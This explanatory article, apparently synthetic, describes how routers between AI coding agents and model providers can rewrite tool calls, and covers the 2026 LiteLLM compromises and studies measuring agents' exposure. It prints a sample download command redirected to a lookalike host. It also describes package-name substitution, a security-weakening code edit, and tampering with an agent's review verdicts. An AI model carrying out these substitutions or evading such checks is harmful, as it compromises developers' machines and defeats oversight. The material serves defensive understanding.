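# Routers that rewrite AI agents' tool calls, and the triggers that hide them from tests

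## How a tool call travels from the model to the machine that runs it

An AI agent is a program that calls a language model in a loop and carries out the actions the model requests. The stakes are highest for coding agents, which read and edit files, run shell commands and install software packages on a developer's computer. The model runs on the servers of a provider such as OpenAI or Anthropic, so each request for an action crosses the internet as a tool call, a structured message that names a tool and gives its arguments.

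Many agents reach the provider through a router, a service that forwards requests to one or more providers and passes the responses back. Routers are also called relays, gateways, proxies and aggregators. A router can read and change everything it forwards. In *Your Agent Is Mine*, Liu, Shou and colleagues (2026) tested 428 routers from online storefronts and public communities and found nine that put malicious code into tool calls on the way back to the agent. Two of the nine did this only when a certain condition, called a trigger, was met. Following one harmless request from end to end shows where such a change can happen and why the agent does not notice it.

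### One request and its answer

*Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) describes how Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, communicates with the model. In its example, the user asks for an architecture diagram in the project's README file. Codex puts this message into JSON, a plain-text format for structured data, along with general instructions, a description of the working environment and a list of the tools the model may call. One of these is a shell tool, which requires a command and optionally takes a working directory and a time limit. Codex sends the JSON as a web request to the address in its configuration file. OpenAI's server then turns the JSON into a prompt, runs the model and streams the result back.

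The first response contains no diagram, since the model has not yet seen the file. It contains a request to read it. With the directory path and the identifier shortened, the tool call looks like this:

```json
{
  "type": "function_call",
  "name": "shell",
  "arguments": "{\"command\":\"cat README.md\",\"workdir\":\"/code/project\"}",
  "call_id": "call_8675309"
}
```

The command `cat` prints the contents of a file. Nothing has run on the developer's machine yet. Codex now parses the message, takes the command out of the `arguments` field and runs it in the shell. Depending on its settings, the agent may first show the command and wait for approval. Under auto-approval, often called YOLO mode, it runs tool calls without asking, so nobody sees the command before it runs.

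Codex appends the output to the conversation under the same `call_id` and sends the whole conversation back to the model, which may return another command. A single turn can include hundreds of these calls. The loop ends when the model returns an ordinary message to the user, such as confirmation that it has added the diagram.

Anthropic's interface works the same way under other names. According to Anthropic's *How tool use works*, the model "never runs anything on its own." It emits a structured request, and the developer's program runs the tool and returns the result. This repeats for as long as each response carries the stop reason `tool_use`. A few tools, including web search and a code sandbox, run on Anthropic's servers instead, and their output usually returns to the model before any response leaves those servers. A router there cannot replace a command before it runs. But shell commands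 and file edits run on the client side, which Anthropic says accounts for the vast majority of tool-use traffic.

The harm a changed tool call can do depends on what the tools can reach. *The Proxy Knows Too Much* (Xie, Wu and colleagues, 2026) describes the coding agent as the most serious case, because a tool call it executes runs with the developer's authority. A changed command can therefore delete any repository or read any private key that the developer can.

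### What a router does with the traffic

Changing one setting, the address to which Codex sends its requests, puts a router on this path. Any service that implements the same interface can receive those requests, and the agent needs no modification.

According to Xie and colleagues, the router then checks the caller's credential, which the router's operator issued. It picks one of the operator's accounts with providers, attaches that account's key and forwards the request. As the response streams in, the router relays it and records how many tokens (the units of text by which providers bill) the exchange used. Operators also add functions such as per-account limits and switching to another account when one fails.

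People have good reasons to use routers. *Your Agent Has a Middleman You Didn't Vet* (Crosley, 2026), a commentary on the study by Liu and colleagues, quotes their list: fallback from one model to another, load balancing, lower cost, and a single key for many providers. The same passage adds that routers are especially common where direct access to a provider is restricted, expensive or subject to quotas. For companies, Anthropic's *LLM gateway configuration* mentions budgets, usage tracking across teams and an audit log of every interaction with the model. In the set-up Anthropic shows for its agent Claude Code, each developer holds only a credential for the gateway, which holds the organisation's credential for the provider. This is arguably more secure than giving everyone the provider's key. The category is therefore very wide, and includes cloud services such as Amazon Bedrock, the open-source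 program LiteLLM, the commercial service OpenRouter, and resellers on the Chinese marketplace Taobao.

All of these routers sit between the agent and the provider, and encryption does not stop them from reading the traffic. Agents and providers protect their traffic with TLS (Transport Layer Security), the protocol that also secures web browsing. When the agent's configuration names a router, the agent's TLS connection ends at the router. The router decrypts the request, opens a second TLS connection to the provider, and encrypts the request again to send it on. The response goes through the same steps in reverse. Even if both connections are secure, the router has the plain text of the whole exchange, including the user's prompts, the contents of files the agent has read, any passwords or keys in them, and the tool calls the model sends back.

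TLS has always guaranteed that a message is intact and authentic only over a single connection. The introduction to RFC 9421, the IETF's February 2024 standard for signing web messages, explains that a path made up of several connections has no such guarantee as a whole.

A request may cross several routers, each of which is called a hop. Crosley retells an example from Liu and colleagues in which a developer buys access from a Taobao reseller, the reseller draws on a larger aggregator, and the aggregator sends its traffic through OpenRouter. The request therefore crosses three routers before it reaches the company that hosts the model. The developer chose only the first, but the other two have the same plain-text access. If either of them changes a response, honest routers that handle it afterwards cannot detect the change.

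### What the person reads and what the agent executes

A model's response usually has two parts, text and a tool call, and only the tool call determines what the developer's program runs. The sample response in Anthropic's *Handle tool calls* contains a text block, "I'll check the current weather in San Francisco for you", and a `tool_use` block with the tool's name, `get_weather`, and an input that gives the location and the unit of temperature. According to the documentation, the program should extract the name, identifier and input from the `tool_use` block and run the corresponding tool. It would look up the weather in San Francisco even if the text block said Paris.

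Luo, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *Rewriting the Response Path*, write the response as *r* = (*x*, *c*), where *x* is the text the developer reads and *c* is the field the agent executes. Fu, Li and colleagues (2026), in *Where Is the Cost of Third-Party API Routers in Agentic Software Development?*, use the same division and point out that a small change to *c* can have a large effect on the project, while an unchanged *x* keeps the record plausible to a reviewer. In the README example, a developer who skims the conversation sees a remark about reading a file, regardless of what command the shell received.

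The agent's own checks don't catch a well-formed substitution. A program can check only whether the JSON of an incoming tool call parses, whether the named tool exists and whether the arguments have the right types. Codex's shell tool, for example, requires a command, and any command meets that requirement. The router can get the correct form from the agent's tool definitions, which pass through it with the request. The call's identifier doesn't expose the substitution either, because it only pairs a result with its call, and a router can change the arguments without changing the identifier. TLS confirms that the message came from the router but can't show whether the router altered it.

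Luo and colleagues define the missing check formally. Let auth<sub>S</sub>(*c*) equal 1 if model *S* really produced the field *c*, and let exec(*c*) be the act of executing it. A safe agent would perform exec(*c*) only where auth<sub>S</sub>(*c*) = 1. On a direct connection to the provider, this condition holds without a test because no other party can write the field. With a router on the path, the condition can fail, and the agent still executes any substitute *c′* of valid form just as it would the original. They call this the response-path integrity gap and attribute it to the design. It exists even when every router on the path is honest, because the agent has no more proof of where its commands came from than it would with a dishonest router.

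Tool calls generally seem to go unverified. According to Luo and colleagues, providers attach nothing to a tool call that would let the recipient verify it, and Claude Code, Cursor, Cline and Continue execute tool calls without checking their origin. Crosley reports that Liu and colleagues ran Claude Code, Codex, OpenCode and OpenClaw through their own router, and that none of them checked the origin either. The two groups include seven different agents, since Claude Code is in both.

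In Bolin's example, the response contains a readable tool call and a record of the model's reasoning, part of which is encrypted so that OpenAI's server can decrypt it when the agent sends it back. The tool call cannot be encrypted this way because the agent has to read it to act on it. The provider could instead sign the tool call, which would keep the command readable and make any change to it detectable.

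### Prompt injection and network interception

Payload injection means changing or adding a tool call after the model produces its response and before the agent receives it. Two better-known attacks resemble it, but defences against them do little to stop it.

In prompt injection, the attacker manipulates the model, usually through instructions hidden in a document, web page or tool output that enter its context and change its behaviour, as Fu and colleagues describe. If a README file told AI systems to upload the developer's keys and the model obeyed, the harmful tool call would be the model's own output, and better training might have prevented it. In payload injection, an intermediary changes the tool call after the model generates it, so the model may have behaved perfectly. The model might request `cat README.md`, and the provider's record would show that command, but the shell would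 receive a different one. Luo and colleagues observe that training a model to refuse harmful requests constrains what the model generates, but not what an intermediary writes afterwards.

A router that rewrites tool calls could in principle also add instructions to the prompt, since it handles the request as well as the response. A defender could detect payload injection by comparing the call the model produced with the one the agent received. That comparison would not reveal an altered prompt, because the misled model produces the harmful call itself and the two copies match.

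Network interception is the other related attack. An outsider, such as someone who controls a public wireless network, tries to get between two parties that are communicating over TLS. The attacker must break the encryption, forge a certificate or divert the traffic at the level of internet routing, and TLS is designed to make that hard. A router does not need to do any of this, because the user entered its address and supplied a credential, so the certificate it presents is genuine. Stricter forms of TLS do not help, for the same reason. Crosley quotes Liu and colleagues on two of them, mutual TLS (both sides present certificates) and certificate pinning (the client accepts only a certificate it already knows): both establish that the agent has reached the router its user chose, but neither verifies that the tool call arrived unaltered.

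Encrypting everything between the agent and the provider would restore integrity, but it would also hide the fields the router needs to decide where to send a request. Luo and colleagues note that this defeats the purpose of having a router unless the protocol separates those fields from the encrypted content. In their account, users let the router read their traffic so that it can route requests, but never gave it permission to alter the executed content. Even honest routers, however, often rewrite the JSON of a tool call in a slightly different form with the same meaning. A difference between what the provider sent and what the agent received is therefore evidence of tampering only if it would change what the agent does.

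### How many agents use routers

In the abstract of their paper, first posted in May 2026, Luo and colleagues write that "roughly 88%" of mainstream agents use the bring-your-own-key configuration, in which users supply their own credential and can point the agent at a router. They report a different number in the body of the paper. Of the 60 most-used applications on OpenRouter, they judged that a custom address was applicable to 25, and found that 23 of those 25 (92%) accept either the user's own credential or a custom address. The abstract may preserve an earlier count, since 22 of 25 would be exactly 88%, but this is a guess.

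The larger problem is that the survey counted applications that accept a custom address, without measuring whether they use one or how much traffic they carry. The sample also came from a router's list of its most-used applications, which is bound to favour software that works with routers. The 23 applications are good evidence that the option is a standard feature of interactive agents, but they do not show that 88% or 92% of agents send their tool calls through an intermediary.

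Download counts reflect actual use more closely. In July 2026, Fu and colleagues reported that LiteLLM had about 40,000 stars on GitHub, the code-sharing site, and that its packaged version had been downloaded more than 240 million times from Docker Hub. For New API, another open-source router, they give 25,400 stars and 1.25 million downloads. Luo and colleagues give New API more than 40,000 stars, which may reflect a different counting date. Fu and colleagues also report that OpenRouter offers over 400 models from more than 60 providers. Xie and colleagues, citing Liu and colleagues in June 2026, report tens of thousands of installations of the most widely deployed open-source template.

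Neither stars nor downloads can be converted into a number of users, because stars record interest and automated systems may download the same package many times. Fu and colleagues write that a growing share of agent traffic in production crosses at least one intermediary, which is plausible given these totals, but they give no percentage. The figures show that routers are ordinary infrastructure in 2026, but not what fraction of the world's tool calls pass through one, or how many of those go through a company's own gateway rather than a stranger's.

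## Finding every intermediary on the path, and how each can turn hostile

A model's response doesn't list the routers that handled it, and the agent's configuration contains only the first router's address. Finding out who could have changed a tool call therefore requires reconstructing the path from configuration files, software records and the operators' answers.

### How to list the parties on the path

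The list starts at the agent and works towards the provider.

1. Read the address that each agent is actually using. Codex takes it from `openai_base_url` or from a `[model_providers.*]` block in its `config.toml` file, as Daniel Vaughan's *Router-Side Injection* (2026) explains. The address may belong to the user's own employer, since a corporate proxy can intercept the same traffic. Write down the company or person behind the address as well as the domain name.
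2. Ask that operator where it sends requests. The answer has to cover every upstream service it might use, including the fallbacks. Xie and colleagues describe routers that choose among a pool of accounts according to their health and then keep a session on the same account, so a test request shows at most one of the possible paths. If an upstream is itself a router, ask its operator the same question, and continue until the answer is an account held directly with the provider.
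3. Identify the software at each hop, its exact version and how the operator installed it. Look inside other products too. TechRadar's *Security flaws found in top open source AI gateway* passes on a warning from the security company Check Point that many platforms and internal tools embed LiteLLM, which may therefore run where nobody set up a gateway on purpose. The list should also include the packages that the software depends on and the tools that its developers use to build and release it.
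4. List the people and accounts with control over each hop. These include the router's administrators, anyone with access to its server, and anyone who can publish a new release of its software. Ordinary users of a shared gateway belong on the list as well, because several flaws found in 2026 let them become administrators.

Logging systems receive copies of the traffic and cannot change a response, but the data they store can help an attacker take over a system that can. In March 2026, LiteLLM (2026) found that one of its features could write plaintext credentials into spending logs and monitoring traces.

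Some operators will refuse to answer, and a dishonest one may lie. If an operator doesn't answer, the user should treat any intermediary beyond it as an unknown party that can change commands. Crosley suggests basing trust in an operator on something outside the router, such as a known team, a contract, or a jurisdiction where the user can enforce a contract. He excludes marketplace reviews.

The list also goes out of date, because a software update can change how a router treats traffic without anyone intending harm. In July 2026, two LiteLLM releases began moving part of Claude Code's requests to a different field before forwarding them to Amazon Bedrock. The model's answers stayed correct for the six days this lasted, but the change broke the caching that lowers the price of repeated prompts. According to LiteLLM (2026), daily spending rose two to three times for the customers who reported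 it, and the problem showed up only in the cache statistics and the bill. A user therefore can't rely on noticing when a router alters requests.

### Four hops, one of them visible

The second step of the procedure gets difficult when the path is long. In the earlier example, the developer's requests pass through a Taobao reseller, an aggregator and OpenRouter before reaching the model's host. Liu and colleagues count these as four hops, although only the first three are routers.

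Because each router forwards the request under its own credential, each party can identify its direct customer and its direct supplier, and usually nobody else:

| Party | Whose credential arrives with the request | What the party could tell the developer |
|---|---|---|
| Reseller | The developer's | Which aggregator it uses |
| Aggregator | The reseller's | That it buys from OpenRouter |
| OpenRouter | The aggregator's | Which host ran the model |
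| Host of the model | OpenRouter's | Nothing that connects the request to the developer |

Suppose the aggregator changes a command. The host and OpenRouter handled the original, but any record they keep is under someone else's account, and neither has a reason to connect it with this developer. The reseller forwards the altered command in good faith. To the developer, the reseller appears to have made the change, but switching to another reseller that uses the same aggregator wouldn't fix the problem. The reseller could also move to a worse aggregator at any time without any change in the developer's configuration.

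A direct connection to the provider removes all three routers. For developers who can't get one, the most useful request to make of a seller is a written list of its upstreams and notice before the list changes. A seller that can't supply this probably doesn't know the full path its traffic takes.

### Dishonest operators

An operator may run a router in order to tamper with its traffic. Liu and colleagues found nine routers that delivered injected malicious code, but they tested from the client's end, so they couldn't tell whether a router's operator or a supplier further upstream had changed the command. Some of the nine routers may have been run by honest sellers who unknowingly passed on a supplier's changes.

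The user is in the same danger whether or not the operator is honest, but the remedy differs. A user can solve the problem by dropping a dishonest operator, while an honest one can fix its own path if someone tells it about the problem. In either case, payment is weak evidence of safety. One of the nine was a paid service, and Liu and colleagues conclude that paying for access makes the service more stable but does not prove that tool calls arrive intact.

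### Honest operators with a poisoned upstream

Liu and colleagues also studied how a benign router can expose its users. They first leaked one of their own OpenAI keys on Chinese forums and in WeChat and Telegram groups that router operators frequent. Other people then used the key to generate 100 million tokens from GPT-5.4, and the traffic exposed more than seven Codex sessions. According to Help Net Security's *Command integrity breaks in the LLM routing layer*, at least one of those sessions contained several credentials.

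The researchers could not always tell from the provider's logs who had used the leaked key. Crosley reports from the full paper that it might have been a router operator using it directly, unrelated people, or someone reusing it deep inside a chain of relays. The study therefore does not prove that any particular router resold the key, but it does show how widely one leaked key can spread and that its owner can end up seeing strangers' work.

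The leaked key is also weaker evidence about tool calls than about secrets. The owner of the account behind a key may be able to read what passes through the account, but owning it doesn't put them between OpenAI's servers and the agent. They would still need control of a router to change a command.

In the other study, the researchers did gain a place on the path, by setting up decoy relays that were deliberately easy to break into. They ran vulnerable copies of claude-relay-service on 20 domains, and copies of Sub2API and CLIProxyAPI with weak passwords on 20 IP addresses. The decoys received more than 40,000 unauthorised access attempts from 147 addresses. Liu and colleagues interpret these as a mixture of automated scanning and people reusing relays, so the number is a poor measure of targeted attacks.

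Later, router operators or others who had found the decoys began using them as upstreams for real agents. The decoys served about 2 billion tokens, and about 13 GB of prompts and responses passed through them in readable form. The traffic contained 99 different credentials and came from 440 Codex sessions across 398 projects or hosts. A user at the start of one of these paths had no way to see that the request would reach a machine with a weak password, run by researchers.

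All 440 sessions were open to command injection by a relay, as the paper defines it. In 401 of them (91%), the user had turned on auto-approval. Liu and colleagues note that an attacker in their position would not have needed a trigger or other disguise in those 401 sessions, because even a plainly altered command would have run without anyone checking it.

The 91% figure covers people whose traffic ended up on badly secured relays, not Codex users in general. People who buy cheap access through several middlemen may well be more casual about approvals than a company with its own gateway. Still, in hundreds of real sessions, the study found an unknown upstream together with an agent that runs commands without asking for approval, the two conditions that make payload injection most dangerous.

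### The LiteLLM compromise of March 2026

A company that runs its own gateway avoids unknown operators but still depends on whoever writes and publishes the gateway's software. On March 24, 2026, attackers published two malicious versions of LiteLLM, 1.82.7 and 1.82.8, on PyPI, the public registry for Python packages. According to LiteLLM's *Security Update* (2026), the versions were available from 10:39 UTC for about 40 minutes before PyPI quarantined them. But LiteLLM warns that anyone who installed or upgraded the package before 16:00 UTC may be affected, so it is safer to search that longer window.

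The malicious code gathered environment variables, SSH keys, cloud credentials, Kubernetes tokens and database passwords, then sent them to a domain that resembled LiteLLM's own. Version 1.82.8 ran this code every time Python started, even if no program loaded LiteLLM, as Boost Security's *TeamPCP Compromises LiteLLM* explains. The malware also spread to Kubernetes clusters, according to *litellm 1.82.8 Supply Chain Attack on PyPI (March 2026)* (2026) by FutureSearch, whose team first reported the release to PyPI.

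Many gateways were unaffected. LiteLLM's official Docker image, which packages the program with everything it needs, used fixed versions of its dependencies and did not use the malicious PyPI packages. People were at risk if they had installed LiteLLM from PyPI without fixing the version, or if they used another product that installed it that way.

The evidence favours stolen credentials as the method of attack. In *Security Townhall Updates*, LiteLLM's chief executive and chief technology officer, Dholakia and Jaff (2026), say attackers obtained the company's release credentials and used them to publish under LiteLLM's real name. Crosley also traces the incident to a stolen publishing token, and Boost Security found that the malicious versions went directly to PyPI, outside the normal release process. According to Crosley, Liu and colleagues call the incident dependency confusion, in which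 an attacker publishes a package under the name of a company's private package and the company's installer fetches the public one by mistake. That term doesn't fit this incident, because users who asked for the genuine LiteLLM package got the attacker's code.

How the attackers obtained the credentials is less certain. Dholakia and Jaff blame Trivy, a security scanner that LiteLLM ran while testing its code. The test system always installed the latest version of Trivy and held long-lived publishing credentials that a compromised scanner could read. The same group, TeamPCP, had compromised Trivy on March 19. According to Help Net Security's *LiteLLM PyPI packages compromised in expanding TeamPCP supply chain attacks* (2026), Trivy's maker, Aqua, attributed that attack to not fully replacing its credentials after an earlier one.

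Boost Security checked LiteLLM's test logs for the poisoned version of the Trivy scanner and found a clean version in every run it sampled between March 19 and 24. A developer's computer or some other job could have fetched the poisoned version instead, so Trivy is still the likely but unproven source. Either way, Trivy belonged on the list of parties that could change a model's response, even though it never handles one.

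LiteLLM's notice and its later explanation both describe an incident in which attackers stole credentials, and neither reports a rewritten tool call. Liu and colleagues cite the incident as payload injection at scale because an attacker who controls the gateway's code can change every tool call that passes through. The attackers did have that ability, since LiteLLM found malicious code inside `proxy_server.py`, which is part of the gateway program. But the public record supports only the theft, not that the attackers also changed responses.

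The attackers also interfered with the warning. A researcher opened a public report on GitHub at 11:48 UTC, and 61 minutes later someone closed it from the chief executive's account, which Boost Security concludes the attackers controlled by then. Automated comments then buried the discussion. An operator who relied on the project's own page for security news would have seen a closed issue full of thank-you messages. Help Net Security's *LiteLLM hit by second supply chain attack this year* (2026) reports that in August the security company Hudson Rock linked a 153 GB archive of data stolen in the attack to 2,488 corporate domains.

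### A signed release with malware in it

LiteLLM rebuilt its release process after March, with separate environments for testing and publishing and signed Docker images. Attackers still compromised it on October 21, 2026, and LiteLLM said its pipeline "built, signed and published" a malicious version, 1.107.0.

According to IT-Administrator's *LiteLLM*, a German trade report, the attackers had credentials from three developers, one of whom owned the organisation's GitHub account. They switched off a protection on the code and directed the release process to a lookalike repository. The official source code for 1.107.0 on GitHub did not contain the malware. The image's signature showed which pipeline had built it, and the attackers controlled that pipeline. A user who read the public code and checked the signature could therefore have found nothing wrong with either.

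This time the Docker images were affected too. Help Net Security reports that the malware was available from 11:39 to 13:23 UTC on PyPI and from 11:46 to 14:20 UTC in the images, including those with the general tags `latest` and `main-stable`. A gateway that pulled a fresh image under either tag during that window could have installed the malware without anyone deciding to upgrade. LiteLLM says that enterprise customers on its private release were not affected.

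The malware looked for login files for Codex, Claude, Gemini and Cursor, and tried to read provider credentials from the databases of LiteLLM gateways. The security firm Socket cautions that this shows what the attackers wanted, not that they succeeded at any particular site. A second component regularly checked a file for the address of more code to run. The file was empty when Socket looked on October 21, but the attackers could have filled it later. About four and a half hours after the theft, researchers at Wiz saw the attackers testing stolen Amazon credentials and checking whether those credentials gave access to AI models. As in March, the reported harm is stolen credentials, and no one has reported a changed tool call.

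Some details of the October attack are provisional. Early coverage, including both reports above, repeats what LiteLLM believed on the first day, that the developers' tokens had leaked into the logs of an internal gateway exposed to the internet. LiteLLM has since marked parts of its early updates as inaccurate or incomplete and published a corrected analysis on October 23. It also replaced its signing key that day and in November began signing releases without a stored key, so anyone who verifies its images needs to update the check.

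### Flaws that hand over a working gateway

Instead of poisoning a release, attackers can break into a gateway that is already running. In 2026, researchers disclosed a series of LiteLLM flaws, most of which an attacker could exploit with only an ordinary user's key. At a company that gives every developer a key to a shared gateway, one dishonest developer, or anyone who obtained a careless developer's key, could have taken control of everyone's traffic.

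Attackers have used one of these flaws, publicly catalogued as CVE-2026-42271, which let any key holder run commands on the gateway's host. CISA, the US government's cybersecurity agency, added it to its list of exploited vulnerabilities in June. Help Net Security's *LiteLLM vulnerability under active attack, CISA warns (CVE-2026-42271)* (2026) reports that Horizon3.ai, a security company, found that a separate flaw in Starlette, a component of LiteLLM, could remove the need for a key. No details of the attacks were public, so it is unknown whether anyone used the access to change responses.

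Obsidian Security's findings provide the most direct link to payload injection. Daily Security Review's *Obsidian Finds CVSS 9.9 Attack Chain in LiteLLM AI Gateway* (2026) reports that in June Obsidian disclosed three flaws in LiteLLM that together let a low-privilege user become an administrator and run code on the server. *LiteLLM Security Alert* (2026), a less reliable secondary account, says Obsidian also found that an attacker could replace a model's response with a forged tool call and alter the input to a safety check so that the check approved the action. An attacker could then do the same harm as a dishonest router from inside a company's own trusted gateway. The account gives no case of an attacker doing this.

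Check Point published two more flaws on October 13. According to Infosecurity Magazine's *Warning Over High-Risk Security Vulnerabilities in Widely Used LLM*, one gave any user access to administrative functions and could lead to a full takeover, while the other exposed the gateway's provider keys. Check Point advises operators to remove unneeded accounts and to test whether limited roles actually restrict what users can do.

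CVE-2026-84377 is a broader version of the key-exposing flaw. Any authenticated user could make the gateway send its provider credentials to a server the user chose, according to the open vulnerability database OSV's entry *CVE-2026-84377* (2026). The entry rates the flaw as medium severity, with a high loss of confidentiality and no loss of integrity. That fits the distinction between a stolen key and a captured router. The thief can spend the company's money at the provider, but the flaw doesn't by itself allow changes to other users' tool calls. OffSeq's *CVE-2026-84377* (2026) reported no evidence of exploitation as of December 1, 2026.

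Two further flaws affect how the gateway decides whom to admit. Dholakia and Jaffer disclosed in *Security Update* that one flaw let attackers interfere with the database query that checks keys. The other let people without a key reach protected management functions under certain conditions. LiteLLM's notice links this second flaw to CVE-2026-48710, the number of the Starlette flaw, but OSV's *PYSEC-2026-388* lists it as CVE-2026-49468, so a search by number may miss it.

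The fixes arrived in different releases:

| Flaw | What was at stake | First fixed release | Source |
|---|---|---|---|
| CVE-2026-35029 | Administrative control | 1.83.0 | LiteLLM |
| CVE-2026-42208 | The database behind the key check | 1.83.7 | Dholakia and Jaffer |
| CVE-2026-42271 | Commands on the gateway's host | 1.83.7 | Help Net Security |
| CVE-2026-59823 | Provider keys | 1.83.9 | Crosley |
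| Obsidian's three flaws | Administrative control and code on the server | 1.83.14-stable | Daily Security Review |
| CVE-2026-49468 | Management functions without a key | 1.84.0 | OSV |
| CVE-2026-84377 | Provider keys | 1.88.6 to 1.96.2, depending on the release line | Crosley |

An operator who followed only one of these warnings could have been left on a vulnerable release. Press coverage of Check Point's findings in October recommended 1.83.9 or later, but 1.83.9 was still vulnerable to Obsidian's attack and to CVE-2026-84377. Crosley checked the affected ranges recorded in eleven LiteLLM advisories on October 1 and found that releases from 1.97.0 onwards fell outside all of them. 1.97.0 is therefore a more sensible minimum, excluding the malicious 1.107.0. He also found that switching off client-supplied credentials, a suggested workaround for CVE-2026-84377, is not enough on its own,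 because an affected release he read was vulnerable with that setting already off.

Even the newest public release of LiteLLM may soon lack fixes that already exist. LiteLLM has announced that it will send fixes for the most severe flaws to some organisations through a private registry before publishing them, because attackers can use AI agents to work out a flaw from its public patch. Until a fix is published, everyone else will run a vulnerable gateway with no public advisory about the flaw.

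## What a rewritten tool call looks like, and what agents do with it

Many changes a router could make to a response would fail, because the agent rejects malformed messages and developers notice absurd ones. The dangerous changes are the ones an agent executes and a busy reviewer accepts. Researchers have described several, and each leaves different parts of the response looking normal.

### Changes a reviewer may meet

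The simplest change replaces a download address. Coding agents often download installers and archives, and the address in the command determines whose software they get. Crosley describes an example from Liu and colleagues in which the router replaces an installer's address in a shell command but leaves the tool's name and the structure of the call unchanged. The two lines below show the same kind of change with placeholder addresses. The provider sent the first line, and the agent received the second.

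```json
{"name": "shell", "arguments": "{\"command\":\"curl -O https://downloads.example.com/setup.sh\"}", "call_id": "call_0001"}
{"name": "shell", "arguments": "{\"command\":\"curl -O https://downloads.example.net/setup.sh\"}", "call_id": "call_0001"}
```

The tool, file name and call identifier are the same in both lines. Only the domain differs, and a developer who sees only the second line has nothing to compare it with. A reviewer can still check whether the address belongs to the project whose software the agent is fetching by opening the project's own documentation in a browser. Asking the agent doesn't help, because its answer comes through the same router.

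In dependency substitution, the router replaces the name of a software package with that of a package the attacker has published. The example that Crosley quotes swaps two letters in the name of `requests`, a widely used Python package. The command still installs from the registry the developer trusts, so checking the domain doesn't reveal the change. Attackers have long registered misspelt package names in the hope that someone will make the typing error, but here the router introduces the error itself.

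The misspelling is visible in the command but easy to miss in a long list of packages. Comparing the command with the project's list of dependencies is a better check, because a package that appears only in the command needs an explanation. An installation that succeeds but leaves the expected package missing also needs one. Crosley adds that the substituted package stays cached for later sessions, so switching to a safe router does not remove it.

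A router can also leave the model's response intact and add a tool call of its own. Fu and colleagues point out that every action the model requested still runs, so the model's explanation still describes those actions accurately. The added call might install a package, write a file outside the scope of the task or run a command that nobody asked for. The clue is an action that the text doesn't account for, such as an installation in the log when the model's text mentions only reading two files. This is only a hint, since a model may request several actions after one short remark. Luo and colleagues mention a more obvious version, in which the router adds a tool call to a response where the model had refused to act, so any action that follows a refusal is worth investigating.

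Replacing the whole response is cruder. As Fu and colleagues define it, the router discards the model's answer and delivers a malicious call with no accompanying text. The log then contains a command without any text and lacks the step the model requested, but neither is easy to notice in a session with hundreds of calls.

A rewritten command can be recognizable by its purpose even when its form looks normal. In one test run by Fu and colleagues, the agent was correcting a false alarm in SQLFluff, a program that checks the style of database queries. It had read the relevant rule and its tests. On the fourth turn, the router made it download and run a script from the internet, which has nothing to do with a style rule. But the command came through the same shell tool as the agent's legitimate commands, and it was not reviewed before it ran.

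The hardest change to notice is an edit to the code the agent is writing. The program still does what the developer asked, but it loses a protection. Luo and colleagues demonstrated this with the production version of Claude Code, which was fixing a small bug in Django, a framework for building websites. The model's code escaped untrusted text before putting it on a page, converting characters that a browser might otherwise treat as code. The router altered one line so that Django skipped this step. This allowed cross-site scripting, in which an attacker's code runs in other visitors' browsers. The comment describing the function stayed the same, all the unit tests passed, and the agent reported a verified fix. The result was the same with all five models the researchers tried.

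A reviewer could catch such an edit in the diff, the list of changed lines. Nothing marks the altered line as foreign, but it belongs to a different function from the one with the bug, and a reviewer who knows Django could well ask why the patch changes it. Luo and colleagues therefore go too far when they conclude that no signal a developer routinely inspects, including the diff, would reveal the edit. Their experiments involved no human subjects, so nobody has measured how often reviewers would notice.

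Both Fu and colleagues and Luo and colleagues also changed the model's explanation to match the altered action, so an explanation that agrees with a command is no evidence that the model requested it. Reviewers should judge the command itself rather than rely on the explanation or the short description that can accompany a shell command. The description is part of the tool call, so a router can rewrite it too. In one sample that Fu and colleagues wrote, a command that steals credential files is described as "Audit and verify credentials".

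### Do altered calls arrive in a form the agent accepts?

An altered tool call does no harm if the agent rejects it as malformed. Liu and colleagues built a router called Mine and used it to test this with OpenClaw, OpenCode, Codex and Claude Code. According to Crosley, they sent 1,000 tool-calling requests through each agent for each type of attack. When Mine rewrote commands, every altered call reached the agent in a valid form. When it substituted package names, 99.6% did.

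These agents are separate programs with their own message formats, so a rewritten call might have failed in one of them, protecting it by accident. The test rules this out, which is not surprising, since the router can see which format each agent expects.

Crosley quotes the researchers' description of the percentages as "compatibility measurements, not end-to-end execution rates", which means they are not success rates. A permission prompt could still have stopped the command, or a sandbox, which restricts what a program can reach, could have limited the damage. The researchers never released their router, Mine, so others would have to build their own to repeat the test.

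### Do agents run them?

Fu and colleagues tested whether four coding agents (Claude Code, Codex, Cursor and OpenCode) block a malicious tool call before running it. Their system, SIDEL, places a controllable router between an agent and its provider. It records an ordinary run, then restarts the agent from the same repository state and replays the recorded responses, altering one on a randomly chosen turn.

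Playing back recorded responses makes the injection the main thing that changes between runs. Language models can give different answers to the same request, so two fresh runs would differ even with an honest router, and it would be hard to tell which differences came from the attack.

Fu and colleagues picked three tasks at random from SWE-bench Lite, a collection of real bug reports from GitHub, each with the project's code and tests. They wrote 400 malicious tool calls by hand, 100 for each of four aims: running malicious code, introducing bugs, stealing private data and compromising the software supply chain. Of these, 277 were shell commands, 74 created files and 49 edited existing files. Each call ran once on each task, giving 1,200 runs for every combination of agent, settings and type of change. The agents worked in isolated containers, so the commands could not harm a real machine.

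No agent blocked an injected call in any of the 19,200 runs, which covered every combination of four agents and four types of change. However, all the agents were in their most permissive modes, such as Full Access in Codex and Run Everything in Cursor, so their settings were not supposed to block the calls.

The tests of stricter settings are therefore more informative. Fu and colleagues also tried Claude Code's `plan`, `acceptEdits` and `auto` modes, Codex's Auto, Cursor's Auto-review and OpenCode's Plan. Each again blocked 0% of calls.

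Claude Code's plan mode is meant to let the agent read files and propose changes without making any. Fu and colleagues explain that it enforces this restriction through the prompt, which affects only what the model requests. A call that the router injects never passes through the model, and the program that executes tool calls did not stop it. Plan mode therefore does not protect a developer who uses it to explore an unfamiliar project from the router. OpenCode's Plan mode blocked nothing either, but the study gives no separate reason.

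Built-in review, in which the agent asks a model to judge a pending action before it runs, has a different weakness. The review request goes through the same router as everything else, so a malicious router can tamper with the verdict as well as the action. Fu and colleagues do not report how many calls got through because of an altered verdict and how many because a reviewer made a mistake or never looked. The difference matters because a separate connection for reviews would prevent only altered verdicts. When the researchers added reviewers with such a connection, those reviewers blocked some of the injected calls but far from all.

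The result for `acceptEdits` is harder to interpret. This setting approves file edits automatically, but more than two thirds of the injected calls were shell commands. Fu and colleagues do not say what happened when a command would normally have needed a person's approval. If the test system approved such commands automatically, the 0% is weak evidence of how this setting performs in ordinary use.

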